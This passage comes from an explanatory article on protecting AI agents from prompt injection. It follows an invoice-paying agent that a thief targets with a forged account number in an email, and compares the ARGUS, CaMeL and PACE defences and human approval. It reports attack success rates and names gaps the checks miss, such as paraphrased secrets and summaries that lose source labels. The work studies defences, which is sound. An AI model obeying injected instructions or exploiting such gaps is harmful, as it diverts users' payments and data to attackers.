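Ma and colleagues built a system called ARGUS on this principle. It keeps a list of required protections that the agent can't change, tries out alternative plans in isolation, and rechecks the requirements just before each sensitive action. In a test of 864 planned runs, 576 had enforcement, and all 97 violations occurred in runs without it.

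Blocking an action can also leave a legitimate task unfinished, so ARGUS can help the agent find another permitted way to complete it. During service failures, this help raised DeepSeek Flash's rate of safely completed tasks by 22.2 percentage points over blocking alone, though the benefit varied between models. In separate scripted tests, some involving payments, ARGUS rejected all 112 operations that relied on outdated authority.

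### Planning before reading

None of the limits on payments described so far depends on who supplied the account number. CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in 2025, tracks this information. With CaMeL, the invoice agent would work as follows:

1. A planning model receives the employee's request but none of the emails. It writes a short program that opens each invoice, extracts the payee and amount, makes the payment and updates the ledger.
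2. An interpreter, which is software that carries out a program step by step, runs this code.
3. When the program needs information from an email, the interpreter passes the text to another model that has no tools. This model returns values such as an amount or an account number.
4. The interpreter labels each value with its source, and carries the labels over to anything the program computes from it.
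5. Before each tool call, the interpreter compares the labels with a policy. For example, the policy could refuse any payment to an account number that came from an email.

The planning model never reads the email, so the email can't add a step to the program, but it can supply a false account number. If the policy accepts account numbers from emails, the thief gets paid. If the policy accepts only numbers from the register or the employee, the agent refuses to pay the thief, but it also refuses when a real supplier announces a new account by email. An employee can then confirm the new number and type it into a request, and the agent can use it immediately, whereas a fixed list of accounts would need an update first.

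Odersky and colleagues reproduce CaMeL's results on AgentDojo for Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini. In 1,926 trials, one attack succeeded. In seven of the eight combinations of model and setting, the agents completed between 48.6% and 81.4% of their tasks. In the eighth, travel tasks with Gemini, they completed 1.4%. With o4-mini, CaMeL completed more tasks than TACIT in all four settings, so CaMeL's extra restrictions don't always make an agent less useful.

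CaMeL's programs can use only part of Python, without recursion or functions that the planning model defines. Odersky and colleagues also argue that the labels disappear if a value enters a model's conversation as ordinary text, for example in a summary. Their own system competes with CaMeL, but the objection is reasonable because a model's summary doesn't show which words came from which source.

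The fixed plan is a bigger restriction for many office tasks. Suppose an email from a real supplier says that its invoices are now on a website. An ordinary agent could visit the website, but CaMeL's planning model wrote its program before the email was opened, so the program has no step for visiting it.

### Checking each call against the user's request

PACE lets a single model read and plan in the usual way, and checks every tool call immediately before it runs. Li, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *PACE*, describe four stages:

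1. PACE freezes the call so that its arguments can't change. It looks up where each argument came from and lists the effects of the call, such as a payment of 300 euros to a particular account.
2. It applies two checks. A path check looks for any route by which untrusted text or secret data could reach a dangerous effect. An authority check compares each effect with rights that PACE has derived from the user's own request, including limits on resources, arguments, budget and time.
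3. It allows the call, blocks it or changes it to a safer form.
4. It records the result and its source, so that it can check later calls.

The paper's proofs apply to a strict version of PACE, but the researchers ran all their experiments on a looser one. The looser version can restore a call that the path check blocked if the authority check accepts it. It can also repair a call without rechecking it. The proofs therefore cover the tested system only when its final action meets their conditions.

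Li and colleagues compared PACE with CaMeL and other defences on three models: Qwen-3.8-27B, DeepSeek-V4-Flash and gpt-5.6-luna. The table gives the success rate of the most effective group of attacks, then the share of user tasks completed.

| Benchmark and model | No defence | CaMeL | PACE |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, Qwen | 48.0% / 62.6% | 0.3% / 35.1% | 0% / 59.7% |
| AgentDojo, DeepSeek | 99.8% / 75.7% | 28.1% / 60.0% | 5.1% / 75.3% |
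| AgentDojo, GPT | 100% / 73.8% | 36.1% / 57.0% | 8.1% / 72.1% |
| AgentDyn, Qwen | 32.5% / 63.4% | 0% / 0% | 0% / 60.5% |
| AgentDyn, DeepSeek | 19.5% / 65.0% | 5.5% / 3.8% | 0.1% / 63.6% |
| AgentDyn, GPT | 19.5% / 74.8% | 0% / 0% | 0% / 73.6% |

CaMeL completed almost no tasks on AgentDyn, where an agent often has to follow helpful instructions that it finds along the way. One would expect this weakness, because CaMeL writes its plan in advance. Its attack success rates of 28.1% and 36.1% on AgentDojo are harder to explain, since only one attack succeeded in the earlier tests. Li and colleagues used different models, and their attacks or their adaptation of CaMeL may have differed too. They were also comparing CaMeL with their own competing system, so an independent comparison would be useful.

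PACE reduced the share of completed tasks by less than three percentage points in these tests. Across all eight benchmarks, it had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of 79 comparisons and tied for the lowest in 14. It did less well on one version of InjecAgent, another test of hostile text, where 30.8% of attacks on the GPT model succeeded, compared with 50.5% without a defence.

Li and colleagues also tested the parts of PACE separately on 1,167 cases with Qwen. On the AgentDojo cases, the path check alone stopped every attack but reduced the share of completed tasks from 76.8% to 13.6%. The authority check alone also stopped every attack, and the agent still completed 64.6% of tasks, compared with 67.2% with everything switched on. Most of the useful protection therefore came from comparing calls with the user's request rather than from tracking where text came from.

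The same test suggests that PACE can reduce task completion by more than three percentage points. On the test's AgentDyn cases, the share of completed tasks fell from 66.7% to 33.3%. Li and colleagues acknowledge that the small loss they found on the full benchmark doesn't hold for this selection.

The strict version of PACE would probably block every payment by the invoice agent, because each one depends on an email from outside the company. The looser version could restore a payment if the employee's request authorised it, but "process today's invoices" doesn't name any payees. PACE will let the thief's payment through if it treats the request as permission to pay whoever sent an invoice, and it will refuse the real suppliers too if it requires a named payee. The company would have to supply the missing information, for example by connecting PACE to its supplier register.

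The researchers' strongest attack test of PACE didn't cover the misuse of a permission that the agent needs, because every attack goal lay outside what the user had authorised. An automated attacker revised its attacks on 30 goals, with up to 50 attempts at each. It achieved 21 of the goals without a defence and none against PACE. With only 30 cases, the true success rate against PACE could still be as high as about 11%.

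PACE can also fail to track data. It recognises a secret in certain standard encodings, but not if the model paraphrases, translates or splits it. It also cannot detect effects that a tool causes internally without declaring them.

Portico, CaMeL and PACE all check calls before the tool runs. If a compromised HTTP library changes the payee after that check, none of them will detect the change. The accounting host can still reject the payment if it has its own copy of the supplier register.

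### Asking a person to approve each payment

An employee may know things that none of these systems can find out, such as whether the printing firm mentioned a new bank account last week. Requiring the employee to approve each payment could make use of that knowledge. However, Odersky and colleagues write that frequent requests cause fatigue and that people tend to ignore them, though they don't measure this. In the Anthropic study described earlier, only 13.6% of testers refused a clearly dangerous command.

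Suppose the employee refuses each fraudulent payment with the same probability, independently of the others. Some of the thief's payments will go through before the first refusal, and their expected number is

(1 − 0.136) / 0.136 ≈ 6.4.

At 500 euros each, that is about 3,200 euros, unless the daily payment limit stops the thief sooner. A refusal might then lead the company to investigate, so even careless approval gives some protection against a series of thefts. But the chance of stopping any single payment is low, and it could be lower still for invoices, because a changed account number is harder to spot than a dangerous command. The assumption of independence is also doubtful, since an employee who accepts the false account once will probably accept it again.

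If the approval screen shows only the supplier's name and the amount, the forged invoice looks normal to the employee. A summary written by the model could repeat the attacker's claims or leave something out, as Codex's summary did in NVIDIA's test. The screen should take the account number directly from the payment order and show it beside the number in the register. If the two account numbers differ, the employee should call the supplier on a phone number the company already has, because the one in the email may belong to the thief.

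Few people would do this for every payment. Ten payments a day over 250 working days would require 2,500 approvals a year. The company could instead let the agent pay registered accounts without approval and ask the employee to check only changes to those accounts. If suppliers change their accounts 20 times a year and each check takes five minutes, the employee would spend less than two hours a year on checks, instead of more than 200. These figures are invented, but most companies pay their suppliers far more often than their suppliers change banks.

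An approval should also apply only to the exact account and amount that the employee saw. It protects nothing if the agent can change either one afterwards, or if "always allow" covers every later payment. Ma and colleagues recommend checking authority again at the moment of execution, because it may have changed since the agent made its plan. The accounting host could compare the final payment order with the approved one and reject it if the two differ.

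In this arrangement, software can't correct a mistaken approval. Santos-Grueiro trusts an authenticated human decision, which can give an agent new rights, but gives no effect to a model's claim that somebody has approved an action. The thief therefore can't use an email to forge the employee's consent. But if the thief persuades the employee that the new account is genuine, Portico will grant the right to pay it, and the company has to rely on the cap of 5,000 euros a day to limit its loss.
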